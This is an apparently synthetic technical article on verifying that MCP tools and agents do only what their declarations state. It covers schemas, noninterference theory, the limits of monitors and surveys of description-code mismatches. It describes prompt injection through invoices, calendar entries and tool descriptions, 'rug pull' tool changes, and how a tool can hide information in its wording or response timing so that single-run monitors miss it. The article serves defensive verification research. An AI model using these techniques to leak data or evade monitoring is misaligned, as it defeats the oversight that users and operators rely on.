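# Verifying that AI tools and agents do only what their declared interfaces say

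## Tools, agents and the interfaces they declare

A language model on its own produces only text. To search a folder, query a database or pay a bill, it needs a tool, which is a program the model can call. An agent is a language model that runs in a loop, choosing a tool, reading the result and choosing again until the task ends. The model works from the tool's declared interface and seldom sees its code. The declared interface is everything the author has stated about the tool: its name, description, inputs, outputs, permissions and side effects (whatever a call changes or transmits besides returning its result). The people who install the tool usually rely on the same statements.

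Verifying a tool means establishing that it does what its declared interface states and nothing more. Establishing that it does nothing more is the hard part. Testing a currency converter on ten sums can show that it converts them correctly, but not whether it also copies each sum to a stranger's server. The same difficulty arises when an agent hands work to another agent based on that agent's description of itself.

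### From description to call

Models usually connect to tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic published in November 2024. The protocol has three roles. The host is the application a person uses, such as a coding assistant. The client is a connector inside the host. The server is the program that offers the tools, and it may run on the user's machine or a remote one. *Exposed by Design*, a security study (Padilla, 2026), found that more than 21,000 MCP servers were reachable on the public internet by May 2026.

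Suppose a small firm uses an agent to help with its accounts and installs a tool that adds up invoices. The tool's author declares that it reads one folder, returns a total, a currency and a short note, and does not write data or access the network. The tool uses a second language model to read the invoices because suppliers' layouts vary too much for ordinary code to handle.

The client begins by sending the server a `tools/list` request. The server replies with a declaration for each tool it offers, and the one for the invoice tool might look like this:

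```json
{
  "name": "sum_invoices",
  "description": "Adds up one month's invoices. Reads only the folder /invoices. No network access. Writes nothing.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "month": { "type": "string" } },
    "required": ["month"]
  },
  "outputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "total": { "type": "number" },
      "currency": { "enum": ["EUR", "GBP", "USD"] },
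      "note": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 200 }
    },
    "required": ["total", "currency", "note"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  },
  "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true, "openWorldHint": false }
}
```

The host places this description in front of the agent's model together with the user's request. The model receives the text word for word, as *Don't believe everything you read* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) points out, and has no other basis for picking a tool. If the user asks what the firm spent in October, the model matches the question to the description and writes a call containing the tool's name and the argument `"month": "2026-10"`. The client sends the call as a `tools/call` request. The server runs the tool and returns, say, 4310.50, EUR and "Two invoices lack a date." The client passes the result to the model, which answers the user or calls another tool.

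*Tools* (2026), the part of the Model Context Protocol's July 2026 specification that governs tool declarations, allows a server to change its list of tools over time and notify clients that it has. An inspector's approval of a declaration therefore covers only the version inspected. Clients may keep a copy of the list for a limited time, five minutes in the specification's example. The specification also recommends, but does not require, that a person be able to refuse any tool call.

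### What a machine can check and what it cannot

A program can compare a result with the output schema without understanding anything about invoices. It can confirm that the total is a number, that the currency is one of three codes, and that the note is at most 200 characters long. It can also reject a fourth field, but only because the author wrote `"additionalProperties": false`. JSON Schema, the notation for these rules, otherwise lets an object contain extra fields with any content. The `maxLength` line shows a useful habit, which is to replace a word no program can test, such as "short", with a number. Authors can now write more kinds of testable rules because the July revision allows every keyword of the 2020-12 version of JSON Schema, according to the Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026).

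The specification requires servers to return results that fit the schema, but only recommends that clients check them. A result can fit the schema and still be wrong, such as a total of zero when the invoices add up to some other amount. Checking a result against the schema also doesn't show what the tool did before returning it.

Only a tool's prose description covers what the tool does beyond returning a value. "Reads only the folder /invoices" and "No network access" are claims about the tool's behavior, and checking the returned value cannot confirm them. Li and colleagues give the example of a function described as looking up a user's profile by ID. The code looks up the profile, but then also writes the time of the lookup to the database. The caller gets the result it expected, and neither the model nor the user can see the write.

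The four annotations at the end of the declaration seem firmer, because each is either true or false. *Class ToolAnnotations*, part of the documentation for one of the Model Context Protocol's official software kits, defines them as follows.

| Hint | Meaning when true | What clients should assume if it is missing |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool creates, updates and deletes no data in any system | False |
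| `destructiveHint` | The tool may make destructive changes, beyond adding things | True |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | False |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with an unpredictable range of outside parties, as web search does | True |

A program can read these values but cannot confirm them. Each default is the worst case, so filling in a hint can only make the client less careful. If an author carelessly leaves the hints out, the user sees a few extra confirmation dialogs, but a dishonest author gains by filling them in with false values.

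The specification requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from trusted servers, but it leaves clients to decide which servers those are. The Model Context Protocol (2026) maintainers wrote in a March blog post that, in practice, most clients take installation as the sign of trust. This leaves the rule with little effect, since a user has to install a tool before its hints matter. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked during the original review how a client could use a flag that it could not trust. The maintainers now say that hints can help decide when to show a warning, or serve as one input among several to a policy engine. A guarantee that a tool cannot send data out should come from network controls or a sandbox, an execution environment that withholds files, network access or system functions from the program inside it.

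The hints also cannot express "reads only this folder" or "opens no network connection", so for now the two most important statements about the invoice tool exist only as English sentences. The closest hint is `openWorldHint` set to false, but "outside" may mean beyond the machine or beyond the company's network, depending on where the server runs. Richer hints about trust and sensitivity were still draft proposals in the Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* of April 2026, and the project has set its next revision for 30 March 2027.

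Earlier revisions of MCP let a server use the host's language model through a feature called sampling. The July revision deprecates sampling and advises developers to connect directly to a model provider instead, which usually requires network access. A new invoice tool that follows this advice and keeps to "no network access" would have to run its model on the local machine.

### What agents declare about themselves

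Agents advertise themselves to each other through a different standard, Agent2Agent (A2A). Google released it in April 2025, and it reached a frozen version 1.0 in March 2026. An agent publishes an agent card, a file at a fixed address on its web domain. The card gives the agent's name, what it can do, where to reach it and how to log in. Ghumare (2026) stresses in *A2A v1.0*, a guide for developers, that the protocol treats the agent on the other end as opaque, so the caller does not get access to its tools, memory, model or plan.

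An agent card therefore gives a checker less to test against than a tool declaration does. The invoice tool has typed fields, but a card may specify only "text in, text out". The A2A Protocol's *Agent2Agent (A2A) Protocol Specification* calls an agent's listed skills "largely a descriptive concept", meaning behaviours at which the agent is likely to succeed, so the list doesn't limit what the agent may do. The card has no standard field for side effects or for things the agent will not do. A few entries are testable. For example, if a card marks push notifications as unsupported, the agent must answer any request for them with a specific error. A card may also carry a cryptographic signature, which lets a caller confirm who signed it and that nobody has altered it since, but not that its contents are true.

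Agent Skills' *Specification* defines a skill differently, as a folder containing a file called `SKILL.md` and sometimes scripts. The agent loads every skill's name and description at startup, and loads the full instructions once it decides that a skill fits the task. An experimental field lists tools that the skill may use without further approval. Any need for network access goes in an optional free-text field of up to 500 characters. The format's validator checks that the header is well formed and follows the naming rules. `SKILL.md` is an unusual declaration because it both describes the agent's behaviour and produces it, so someone can change what the agent does by editing the instructions while leaving the description unchanged.

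### Four causes of a mismatch

The most ordinary reason a tool does more than its author declared is carelessness. A developer adds a cache, a log or an update to a "last seen" field and never revises the description. The invoice tool's developer might add a crash reporter that sends any unreadable invoice to a bug tracker, making "no network access" false without meaning to deceive anyone. Li and colleagues found substantial mismatches between description and code in about 13% of the 10,240 servers they examined, though a mismatch does not show the developer's motive.

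A dishonest author might write the same code on purpose. This author expects inspection and can plan for it, by having the tool behave well under test or by changing it later. *Systematization of Knowledge* (Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues, 2025), a survey of MCP's risks, describes developers who publish deceptive servers and others who alter a tool's definition after users have installed it, known as a "rug pull". Because the model reads a tool's description as trusted context, an author can also plant instructions there that have nothing to do with the tool.

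Prompt injection, in which a model follows instructions contained in outside text, does not require a malicious tool author. Language models cannot reliably tell a user's instructions from ones that an attacker has placed in a web page or an email. The MCP maintainers cite a demonstration in which researchers combined a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a tool that runs code. In such a chain, each tool can behave as declared while the agent does something that no user asked for. The programmer Simon Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the three conditions that make this kind of data theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. Users often combine tools from several servers, so the danger depends on the whole session and cannot be detected from any single declaration.

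The invoice tool is exposed to prompt injection because it reads documents that strangers write. A supplier could hide a line in an invoice telling the model to put another supplier's bank details in the note. Testing the tool on clean invoices would not reveal this. The note would still be a string of under 200 characters, so whether it broke the declaration depends on how one defines compliance. The note would then enter the context of the firm's own agent, which may well have an email tool.

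The last cause is the model itself, whose behaviour comes from training and was never written down. The model inside the invoice tool might tend to guess a figure when a scan is blurred, or to name suppliers in the note when their invoices are overdue, though no author or attacker intended this. Gaire and colleagues describe a milder version, in which a model misreads its situation and calls a tool with the wrong parameters. A standing tendency is harder to deal with than an occasional error, because it may appear only under conditions that nobody has tried, and there is no line of source code to compare with the description.

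### Finding, preventing and proving

Suppose the crash reporter is in place and an unreadable invoice arrives. An administrator who checks the network log will see the connection and know that the declaration was false, but only after the invoice has left. A clean log is weaker evidence than it appears, since it covers only the runs so far and the kinds of event it records.

If the firm had run the tool in a sandbox without network access, the connection would have failed. This kind of prevention works whether the cause is a bug, a thief, an injected instruction or a learned habit. But it works only on the routes that somebody thought to close, and the note is a route that has to stay open, because returning it is part of the tool's job.

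Proving that a violation cannot occur requires an argument that covers every possible run, starting from stated assumptions. For the network claim, the argument might be that the sandbox passes no connection requests. This proof holds only if the sandbox's own code, the operating system and the hardware, which together make up the trusted base, all work as specified.

The Agentic AI Foundation explains that hardware attestation, in which a processor signs a record of the software it has loaded, establishes which code and policy the machine measured, but not whether the policy was the right one. Attestation therefore does not prove that a tool does only what its interface declares. It also depends on the processor's signing keys staying secret. An attack called TEE.fail extracted these keys from fully patched systems with a device costing less than $1,000, though it required physical possession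 of the machine.

How much assurance a user needs depends partly on the cause of the undeclared behaviour. An honest developer who hears about the crash reporter will remove it, so detection may be enough where the harm is small or reversible. Detection comes too late against a thief, because nobody can recover a copied invoice. If the cause is the model inside the tool, proof is difficult because there is no compact account of the model's behaviour to reason from. The claims about the invoice tool that look easiest to prove concern the restrictions around the model, such as which files it can open, where it can connect and how many characters it can output.

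## What it means to do only what is declared

A tool can exceed its declaration in two ways, and each needs its own rule. It can change or send something that its author never mentioned, as the invoice tool's crash reporter does. It can also put more into its answer than the declaration covers, which leaves nothing unusual in any log.

Under the effects rule, a call may have only the side effects that were declared. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, require the actual effects to be a subset of the declared effects. They treat a failure to do the declared job as a separate fault. A checker should also count file reads. These change nothing, so strictly they are not side effects, but the invoice tool's author declared which folder the tool reads.

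The output rule compares two cases. If two folders have the same declared result, the tool must return the same output for both. Otherwise a person who sees only the output can learn something about the folder that the declared result does not reveal. Let x and x′ stand for everything the tool can read in the two cases, d for the declared result and out for what the tool returns. The rule is then:

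If d(x) = d(x′), then out(x) = out(x′).

A declared transmission is also an output. If the author declares that the tool emails the total to an accountant, the effects rule permits the email and the output rule governs its contents.

A tool can obey either rule while breaking the other. *SINGED* (2026) built counterfeit tools to compare with honest ones and ran every candidate in an isolated sandbox. It kept only the cases in which all the candidates returned the same verified output and only the counterfeit caused an extra effect, so comparing outputs cannot identify the counterfeit. Conversely, a tool with no side effects can slip a supplier's name into its note.

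### From noninterference to permitted release

The output rule comes from noninterference, which *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) defined for a computer with several users. One group of users does not interfere with another if deleting all of the first group's commands from the history would leave the second group's outputs unchanged. Researchers who study programs usually apply the idea to data, so that changing the secret inputs must not affect what an unauthorised observer sees.

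No useful invoice tool satisfies this, because its total depends on the invoices, which the firm wants to protect. Sabelfeld and Myers, in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, discuss the same problem in a program that publishes an average salary. Under their definition, delimited release, the programmer marks certain expressions as releasable, and the program must reveal nothing else about the secret data. The test is that if two starting memory states agree on all public data and on the value of every marked expression, the program's public results must agree too. The output rule is this test with the declared result as the marked expression. Sabelfeld and Myers remark that programmers could list the marked expressions in a separate interface, roughly as a tool declaration does.

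The marked expressions must refer to the original data. Otherwise, an altered salary program could overwrite every salary with that of employee 1 and then publish the average, using the same line of code as before. Suppose two employees earn 2 and 3, and then swap salaries. The true average is 2.5 both times, but the altered program publishes 2 in one case and 3 in the other, so the comparison exposes the attack. An invoice tool could leak one supplier's amount in the same way, by copying it over all the others before adding them up.

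In *Declassification*, Sabelfeld and Sands explain the test as whether the output would tell anything new to an observer who already knew the declared result. The test ignores how much work it would take to recover information from that result. This is awkward when the declared result is a hash, a scrambled code from which recovering the original should be impractical. If a program may release the hash of a password, and no other password has that hash, the test also accepts a program that publishes the password itself, because in principle the hash already identifies it.

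Goguen and Meseguer likewise do not address what people can infer from information they are allowed to have. If the firm received only one invoice in October, the total equals the amount on that invoice, and the output rule still permits the tool to return the total.

### Exact and loose declarations

Suppose the invoice tool's author removes the note and declares exactly how to compute the total and the currency. The output rule then adds nothing to ordinary correctness. A correct tool always returns d(x), so two folders with the same declared result necessarily produce the same output. An inspector who checks each answer against the invoices is checking both things at once. (The reverse does not hold, since a tool that always returns zero reveals nothing and is useless.)

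With the note back in place, the declaration allows a vast number of answers for each folder, and the tool chooses among them. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives a small example of the danger. A system may output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit, and it chooses arbitrarily. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs reveals nothing. If a programmer then builds a version that always outputs the secret bit, it reveals the secret even though the original design allowed every output. A tool with a loose declaration can leak data in the same way, because its choice of answer can depend on private data while every call stays within the declaration. The more answers the declaration permits, the more data can leak.

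Somebody has to decide what the note may depend on before the output rule can be applied to it. On a strict reading, the note may depend only on the total and the currency. The helpful note "Two invoices lack a date" then breaks the rule, because another folder with the same total might have no undated invoices. The author can fix this by declaring that the note reports the number of undated invoices or, better, by replacing the note with a whole-number field.

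Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026) apply a two-run definition like this one to AI agents in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, and acknowledge that specifying what a disclosure may depend on can take substantial human judgement. Language models are not yet a dependable substitute for that judgement. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, reports a benchmark on which only 24.8% to 34.2% of models' translations from ordinary language into a formal planning language were semantically correct. If a tool's declaration is mistranslated, proving that the tool obeys the translation gives little assurance that it obeys the declaration the user read.

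The model inside the invoice tool may word its note differently each time it reads the same folder, so a test that requires identical outputs would reject harmless variation. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, therefore use a probabilistic form of noninterference. For the invoice tool, this means that each possible output must have the same probability for both folders. *PACE* (2026) allows some difference, provided that an observer cannot tell the two cases apart by more than a fixed margin.

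### What a monitor can enforce

A monitor is a trusted program that watches a run and reports or blocks events that break a rule. Whether it can enforce a rule depends on whether the rule is a safety or liveness property. A safety property, such as "never write to the network after reading a file", forbids something bad that an observer could recognise at a definite point in the run and that no later event can undo. A liveness property requires something good to happen eventually, such as the tool returning a total. If the tool hasn't returned the total yet, it still might, so no finite part of the run can prove a breach. Every rule about single runs combines a safety property and a liveness property.

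The effects rule is a safety property. A tool violates it the moment it opens an undeclared network connection, and nothing the tool does afterwards can undo the violation.

Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, proved that a monitor whose only power is to stop a run can enforce only safety properties. Such a monitor must base its decision on the steps of the current run so far, without comparing it to other runs. It cannot allow a violation on the assumption that a later step will correct it, because the run might end first. If it rejects a run, it must do so after a finite number of steps. Any rule that fits these constraints is a safety property.

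Schneider illustrates the limit with a seller who has taken a customer's money. A monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything except delivering the service. But the seller can do nothing, and halting the seller then does not get the service delivered.

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, proved a similar result for gates that approve or block an agent's tool calls before they take effect. Suppose the rule is that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. If the gate approves a payment, the confirmation may never come, but if it blocks the payment, it may disrupt a run that would have complied. A more powerful mechanism could hold the payment back until the confirmation arrives, but the gate has to decide at once.

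Monitors also cannot enforce some safety properties. For example, "answers within five seconds" is a safety property because nobody can undo a missed deadline, but a monitor cannot prevent time from passing. *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) showed that Schneider's formal account had set only an upper limit on what monitors can enforce. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues) refined the theory by distinguishing actions that a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

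### Why one run cannot reveal a breach

The output rule is a property of sets of runs, not of single runs. Suppose the author declares that the note reports the number of undated invoices, and the tool processes two folders that differ in one respect.

| | Folder A | Folder B |
|---|---|---|
| Total | 4310.50 EUR | 4310.50 EUR |
| Undated invoices | 2 | 2 |
| Invoices stamped "final reminder" | 0 | 1 |
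| Note returned | "Two invoices lack a date." | "2 invoices lack a date." |

Both notes are true and well under 200 characters. An inspector with a complete log of either run alone would find nothing wrong. A tool that always wrote "Two" or always wrote "2" would comply with the declaration. Only comparing the two runs shows that the wording depends on the reminder. Anyone who knows the code can tell from the note that the firm is behind on a bill.

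Clarkson and Schneider call rules of this kind hyperproperties. An ordinary property is a set of permitted traces, where a trace is the ordered record of events in one run. A system satisfies the property if all its traces are in the set. A hyperproperty is a set of permitted systems, each represented by the set of all its traces, so it can restrict how one run relates to another. A limit on average response time across all runs is a hyperproperty, because whether one slow answer is acceptable depends on how fast the others were. For a tool without randomness, the output rule is a 2-safety hyperproperty, which means that a pair of runs is enough to show a violation.

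Pandey and colleagues proved that if a monitor looks at an agent's runs one at a time and never raises a false alarm, it cannot detect any breach of such a rule. Any single run could have come from a compliant system, so a monitor that never flags compliant behaviour can't flag any run. The result matters only where the declaration leaves some freedom in the output.

The researchers illustrated this with a scheduling assistant that may share when its user is free but not why the user is busy. The assistant offers slot 10 if a busy period is an ordinary meeting and slot 11 if it is a confidential interview. Nine language models, including GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8, judged the assistant's actions one at a time, in 30 trials each. Eight models never objected, and the ninth objected in three trials. When shown both runs together, eight models flagged the pair every time, and Meta's Llama-4-Maverick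 did so in 17 of 30 trials. A better model would not have fixed the single-run result, because a single run does not show that the slot offered depends on why the user is busy.

A monitor can still prevent leaks by enforcing a stricter rule, but it will also block some runs that leak nothing. One of Schneider's examples is a ban on sending messages after reading a file. If the firm applied that ban to the invoice tool's answers, the tool could never answer. Pandey and colleagues suggest preventing leaks by generating each disclosure from the authorised information alone. In the invoice tool, a separate program that receives only the number of undated invoices could write the note.

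Another approach, self-composition, is to prove something about both runs at once. The checker joins two copies of a program, starts them with matching public data and matching declared results, and tries to prove that their outputs match. This turns a question about pairs of runs into a safety question about single runs of the combined program, which standard proof methods can handle. But it requires an adequate model of both runs, and *PACE* points out that a tool's code may not capture how an agent chooses the tool's inputs. *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* (Chalupa, Henzinger and Oliveira da Costa, 2025) proposes monitors that construct a run using functions supplied with the specification, then compare it with a real one.

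The firm could also test the tool on pairs of prepared folders. If the tool has no randomness, one mismatch proves a breach, but matching results can't rule one out because other pairs remain untested. If the tool contains a language model, the firm would have to run it on each folder many times and compare how often each result occurs. Pandey and colleagues show that no finite sample can settle that comparison with certainty for every possible agent.

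### What no checker can decide

No method can always determine from a tool's source code, before the tool runs, whether it will follow both rules. This follows from Rice's theorem, which the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953. The theorem covers any property of what programs compute that some programs have and others lack. No algorithm can decide correctly, for every program, whether the program has such a property.

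Side effects raise the same obstacle. If a checker could always tell whether a tool will ever open a network connection, it could also tell whether any given program that makes no connections of its own will finish. It would only have to check a tool that runs the program to the end and then opens a connection, because that tool opens a connection exactly when the program finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can tell whether every such program finishes.

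The theorem concerns all programs at once, but many individual programs are easy to check. Conservative checkers take advantage of this by accepting only programs they can show to comply. They reject everything else, including some that do comply.

Sabelfeld and Myers designed a checker of this type. To block the salary attack, it rejects any program that changes a variable before releasing it. But it also rejects a program that replaces a secret number with its parity (whether it is odd or even) and then releases the result. That program is harmless because it reveals less than the whole number, which the programmer had permission to release. The checker would likewise reject an invoice tool that converts dollar amounts to euros before adding them up.

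A rejection from a conservative checker is therefore weak evidence of wrongdoing. Programmers can sometimes satisfy the checker by rewriting the program, in this case by computing the parity inside the release statement. Acceptance is much stronger evidence of compliance, because a sound checker accepts a program only if every run follows the rule.

### Hard cases

Shi and colleagues describe a weather tool that keeps an undisclosed usage log. It returns the forecast, but it also saves the city's name in a local history, updates the user's profile and reports the query to an analytics service. The developer may see these as ordinary personalisation, but each one breaks the effects rule, whatever the motive. A user would probably mind the analytics report more than the local file. The history could also lead to a breach of the output rule. If the tool uses one query to shape later recommendations,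 a second person on the same account might learn what the first one asked. A fair test has to treat everything the tool stores as part of its input.

A cache is harder to judge. A file-search tool might index the whole disk so that later searches run faster. The index is a lasting change, so it makes the statement "Writes nothing" false, but few users would call it misconduct. Shi and colleagues classify such an index as excessive resource use, which counts as a mismatch only above some threshold that somebody has to choose. Exempting private storage that no other program reads could still allow leaks. If the tool caches search results, repeated searches run faster, and a person who times them may discover that somebody else has already searched for a particular name. It is simpler for the tool's author to declare the cache, with its location and maximum size.

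Response time can also reveal information on a first call. If the invoice tool takes a second to read three invoices and a minute to read 300, a caller can estimate the number of invoices from the delay, even when the totals match. Goguen and Meseguer assume that their output function includes everything the system gives a user, so whether this breaks the output rule depends on whether the function covers timing. The tool complies if timing is left out, but almost every real program fails if it is included. The tool's author could declare that response time depends on the number of invoices, or make every call take the same time, long enough to read the largest folder.

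Garby and colleagues' guarantee, like most others of its kind, does not cover what an observer can learn from whether a run finishes. This usually leaks only about one bit per run, but they point out that an agent with an unmonitored retry loop can repeat the leak until it has revealed the whole secret.

The wording of an answer poses the same problem. Pandey and colleagues tested whether Claude Sonnet 4.6, acting as a scheduling assistant, would leak why its user was busy. Their first analysis found a leak, but the assistant had offered identical slots in both conditions, and the apparent signal came from a word in its phrasing. They decided not to count phrasing and reported no leaks in 80 runs. That was reasonable for their question, but the invoice tool that switches between "Two" and "2" would pass under the same rule, so the rule is unsafe if the tool's author might be hiding messages.

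A shopping search tool might quietly favour one seller while always returning a list of products with prices, as its schema requires, and causing no side effects. If the tool's author declared that results are sorted by price, a single run can expose the bias by showing a more expensive product above a cheaper one. A declaration that promises only "relevant products" permits any order, so no single list can break it.

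The output rule can help if the author also declares what the ranking may depend on, such as price, customer rating and match to the query. An inspector can then swap two sellers' names, keep everything else the same and see whether the order of the products changes. This works even though the sellers' names are not secret, because it tests what the output depends on. It cannot reveal the motive, since a tool that breaks ties alphabetically could fail the test, as could one whose author took a bribe. If the author never declared what the ranking may depend on, favouring a seller does not violate the declaration, and the user can object only to the declaration itself.

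## Comparing a tool's description with its code

An inspector who has a tool's source code can compare it with the description and look for anything the author left out. In the invoice tool, the inspector would see the line that sends unreadable invoices to a bug tracker. This is slow, so researchers who wanted to compare thousands of tools had language models do most of the reading.

### Seven kinds of mismatch

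Shi and colleagues call a disagreement between a tool's description and its code a description-code inconsistency. They sort these inconsistencies into seven types and illustrate the types with a tool that searches for files.

| Type | Description | What the code does |
|---|---|---|
| Undeclared functionality | "Search local files by name" | Also searches cloud storage and adds the matches |
| Overclaimed functionality | "Search local and cloud files by name" | Searches local files only |
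| Misclaimed functionality | "Search local files by name" | Deletes the named file |
| Ambiguous functionality | "Process local files" | Searches local files by name |
| Resource overconsumption | "Search local files by name" | Indexes the whole disk, then searches |
| State mutation | "Search local files by name" | Gives every user of the machine full access to the folder, then searches |
| Data leakage | "Search local files by name" | Searches, then uploads the query to a remote server |

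The top four types concern the job the tool does, and the other three are undeclared side effects. Not every type breaks the rule that a tool should do nothing beyond its declaration. A tool that overclaims usually does less than its author promised, and an ambiguous description may set no definite limit for the tool to exceed.

Overclaiming can still be dangerous, because the missing feature may be a safeguard. Shi and colleagues found a tool for placing orders on a trading exchange that was described as asking for the user's approval first, but its code submitted the order without asking. Another tool was described as converting a "local PDF file" to text, but it uploaded the file to an outside service. A third was supposed only to echo a message, but it added a secret key from the server's settings to the reply. Nobody would find that leak by looking for unexpected connections or file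 changes, since the key was sent in the tool's ordinary reply.

### How DCIChecker works

Shi and colleagues built a program called DCIChecker to find these mismatches in tools written in Python. It reads the code without running it.

The comparison starts by recovering the description that the agent's model would receive. Some developers write one explicitly. Others rely on the MCP software development kit, which copies the comment at the top of the tool's main function. If there is no comment, the model receives no description, as was the case for 2,170 of the 19,200 tools that the researchers collected.

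DCIChecker then gathers the code that a call can reach. The main function often does little itself, so the checker follows its calls to other functions in the same project, up to three layers deep. About 85% of the tools in the researchers' depth analysis needed no more than two layers. The checker also makes a separate list of sensitive operations, such as network requests and file deletions, with their arguments. If the program works out a web address only while running, the list contains a placeholder. For the invoice tool, the collected code would include the function that reads the folder, the function that calls the language model, and the crash reporter's network request.

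Next, DCIChecker gives the description and the code to a language model (Claude Sonnet 4.5) twice, asking once whether the two are consistent and once whether they are inconsistent. It asks both ways because a model's answer tends to lean towards whatever the question suggests. Each time, the model must either name a type of mismatch or answer that there is none, and give its reasons.

If the two answers report the same type of mismatch, or both report none, DCIChecker accepts them. Otherwise it sends both sets of reasons to the model with a third prompt, which tells the model to examine the code for itself and decide whether the alleged mismatch is significant or "a trivial nitpick".

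The researchers checked 400 results by hand and found 197 real mismatches. The prompt that looked for consistency caught only 93 of them. The prompt that looked for inconsistency caught all 197 but raised 53 false alarms. With arbitration, DCIChecker caught 192 and raised 8 false alarms. The published figures imply that in all five misses, one prompt had found the mismatch and the arbitrating model dismissed it. Arbitration cleared 50 pairs in the sample, so an inspector who wanted to miss fewer mismatches could read only the cleared pairs by hand and expect about one in ten to be a real mismatch.

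These tests did not involve tool authors who were trying to fool the checker. A tool's author writes both the description and the code that the checker's model reads, and could add a comment telling the model that the code is safe. *When Neither Side Confirms* (2026), a study of how MCP software handles destructive tools, used a coding guide with a warning to treat source code as untrusted data and ignore any instructions inside it. The prompts that Shi and colleagues published contain no such warning.

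### How common mismatches are

The 19,200 tools came from 2,214 servers, and 17,030 of the tools had both a description and code to compare. DCIChecker flagged 1,907 of these pairs, or 11.2%. (The paper's headline figure of 9.93% includes tools with no description in the total.) Flagged tools appeared on 775 servers, or 35%, and 183 of those servers accounted for 60% of all flagged tools.

Wrong or unclear functionality made up 75.2% of the cases, including 35.4% for overclaiming alone. Undeclared side effects made up the other 24.8%, or about 473 tools (2.8% of the usable pairs). The true number is probably higher, because a tool with both kinds of fault counts only under its main one.

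These counts depend on how many mismatches DCIChecker misses. In the hand-checked sample, it caught 192 of the 197 real mismatches, a recall of 97%. But the sample contains 200 flagged pairs and 200 unflagged ones, whereas unflagged pairs outnumber flagged ones by almost eight to one in the full set. Misses occur only among unflagged pairs, so the sample greatly underrepresents them. Applying the sample's error rates to the full set corrects for this.

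| | Flagged | Not flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Pairs in the hand-checked sample | 200 | 200 |
| Real mismatches in the sample | 192 (96%) | 5 (2.5%) |
| Pairs in the full set | 1,907 | 15,123 |
| Estimated real mismatches in the full set | 1,831 | 378 |

By this estimate, there are 2,209 real mismatches, or about 13% of the usable pairs. DCIChecker caught 1,831 of them, so its recall would be about 83%.

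Five errors are too few for a precise estimate. A 95% confidence interval for 5 in 200 runs from about 0.8% to 5.7%, so the number of missed mismatches could plausibly be between about 120 and 870. That puts recall between 68% and 94%, and the share of mismatched pairs between 11.5% and 16%. Missed mismatches don't affect the reported precision of 96%, because precision is the share of flagged pairs that are real mismatches.

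Someone choosing a tool may care more about the chance that its description is wrong even though DCIChecker has cleared it, which is about 1 in 40. That figure applies to a typical tool in the survey, and it would be higher if the tool's author had tested it against the checker first.

### Why another survey also found 13%

Li and colleagues reached their figure of about 13% with a different program, MCPDiFF. A language model lists the features a server's code implements, then those its documentation mentions. MCPDiFF turns both lists into vectors, rows of numbers that are close together when two texts have similar meanings, and measures how well the lists agree. Agreement was between 40% and 80% for 1,079 of the 10,240 servers, and below 40% for another 314.

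This figure resembles the corrected one for DCIChecker, but Li and colleagues counted servers, not tools. A server with one inaccurately described tool among twenty accurately described ones could easily pass as a good match. MCPDiFF also ignores any feature that the documentation describes but the code lacks, so it would not flag the missing approval step in the order tool.

MCPDiFF reads documentation files such as the README, which introduces a project to human readers, whereas an agent's model normally receives a separate description of each tool. Li and colleagues report that the documentation for longport-mcp, a server that connects to a brokerage, omitted its functions for placing and cancelling orders. Those functions could still have had accurate tool descriptions.

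Li and colleagues do not report checking their results against hand-labelled servers. Shi and colleagues rebuilt MCPDiFF from its published description and found that it caught 90 of their 197 confirmed mismatches. On artificial examples, it caught 38 of 40 data leaks but 11 of 40 overclaims. This comparison favours DCIChecker, since its developers designed the test around their own seven types. The gap between the programs may be small for somebody worried mainly about stolen data.

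Li and colleagues also found that servers with fewer than ten stars on GitHub, a site where programmers share code, fully matched their documentation 53% of the time, compared with 29% for those with 1,000 to 9,999 stars. But the worst mismatches became rarer as popularity rose, and none of the 19 most popular servers had one.

Studies of agent skills define mismatches in yet other ways. *Why Static Skill Inconsistencies Do Not Equate to Runtime Risks* (2026) concentrates on broken promises and contradictions, the reverse of MCPDiFF's choice, and reports 1,182 confirmed inconsistencies in 575 skills. *SkillConsist* (2026), which tested a detector on 633 skills, also counts undeclared behaviour. Percentages from these studies are therefore hard to compare. A mismatch may also be harmless, as the first title suggests, for example if the code in question never runs.

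### What the source code does not show

Inspectors often have no code to read. Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis*, examined 18,770 servers in the official MCP registry and found that 3,007 (16%) offered a remote address but neither a downloadable package nor a link to source code. Even when a remote server links to its source code, the operator may be running different code.

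Zhang and colleagues showed that descriptions alone can reveal some weaknesses. Their program predicted which tools could carry a prompt injection and identified 94 of the 95 that people had confirmed as vulnerable. This works because a tool that fetches web pages has to pass outside text to the model, however its author writes the code. But the method assumes the descriptions are true, so it cannot test whether they are.

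Even when a tool's source code is available, part of the program may be elsewhere. The tool can download a script and run it. An inspector would see the download command but not the script, which the script's owner could replace the next day. Outside libraries cause a similar problem. DCIChecker does not open them, although 43% of the calls it found at its depth limit went to them. It also treats Python's pickle module as a routine utility, even though pickle can run commands hidden in the data it loads.

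Comparing the description with the code also misses the invoice tool's language model, which has no source code to inspect, only weights, the billions of numbers set during training. DCIChecker could correctly conclude that the code matches the description even if the model mentions overdue suppliers in its notes.

### Change after approval

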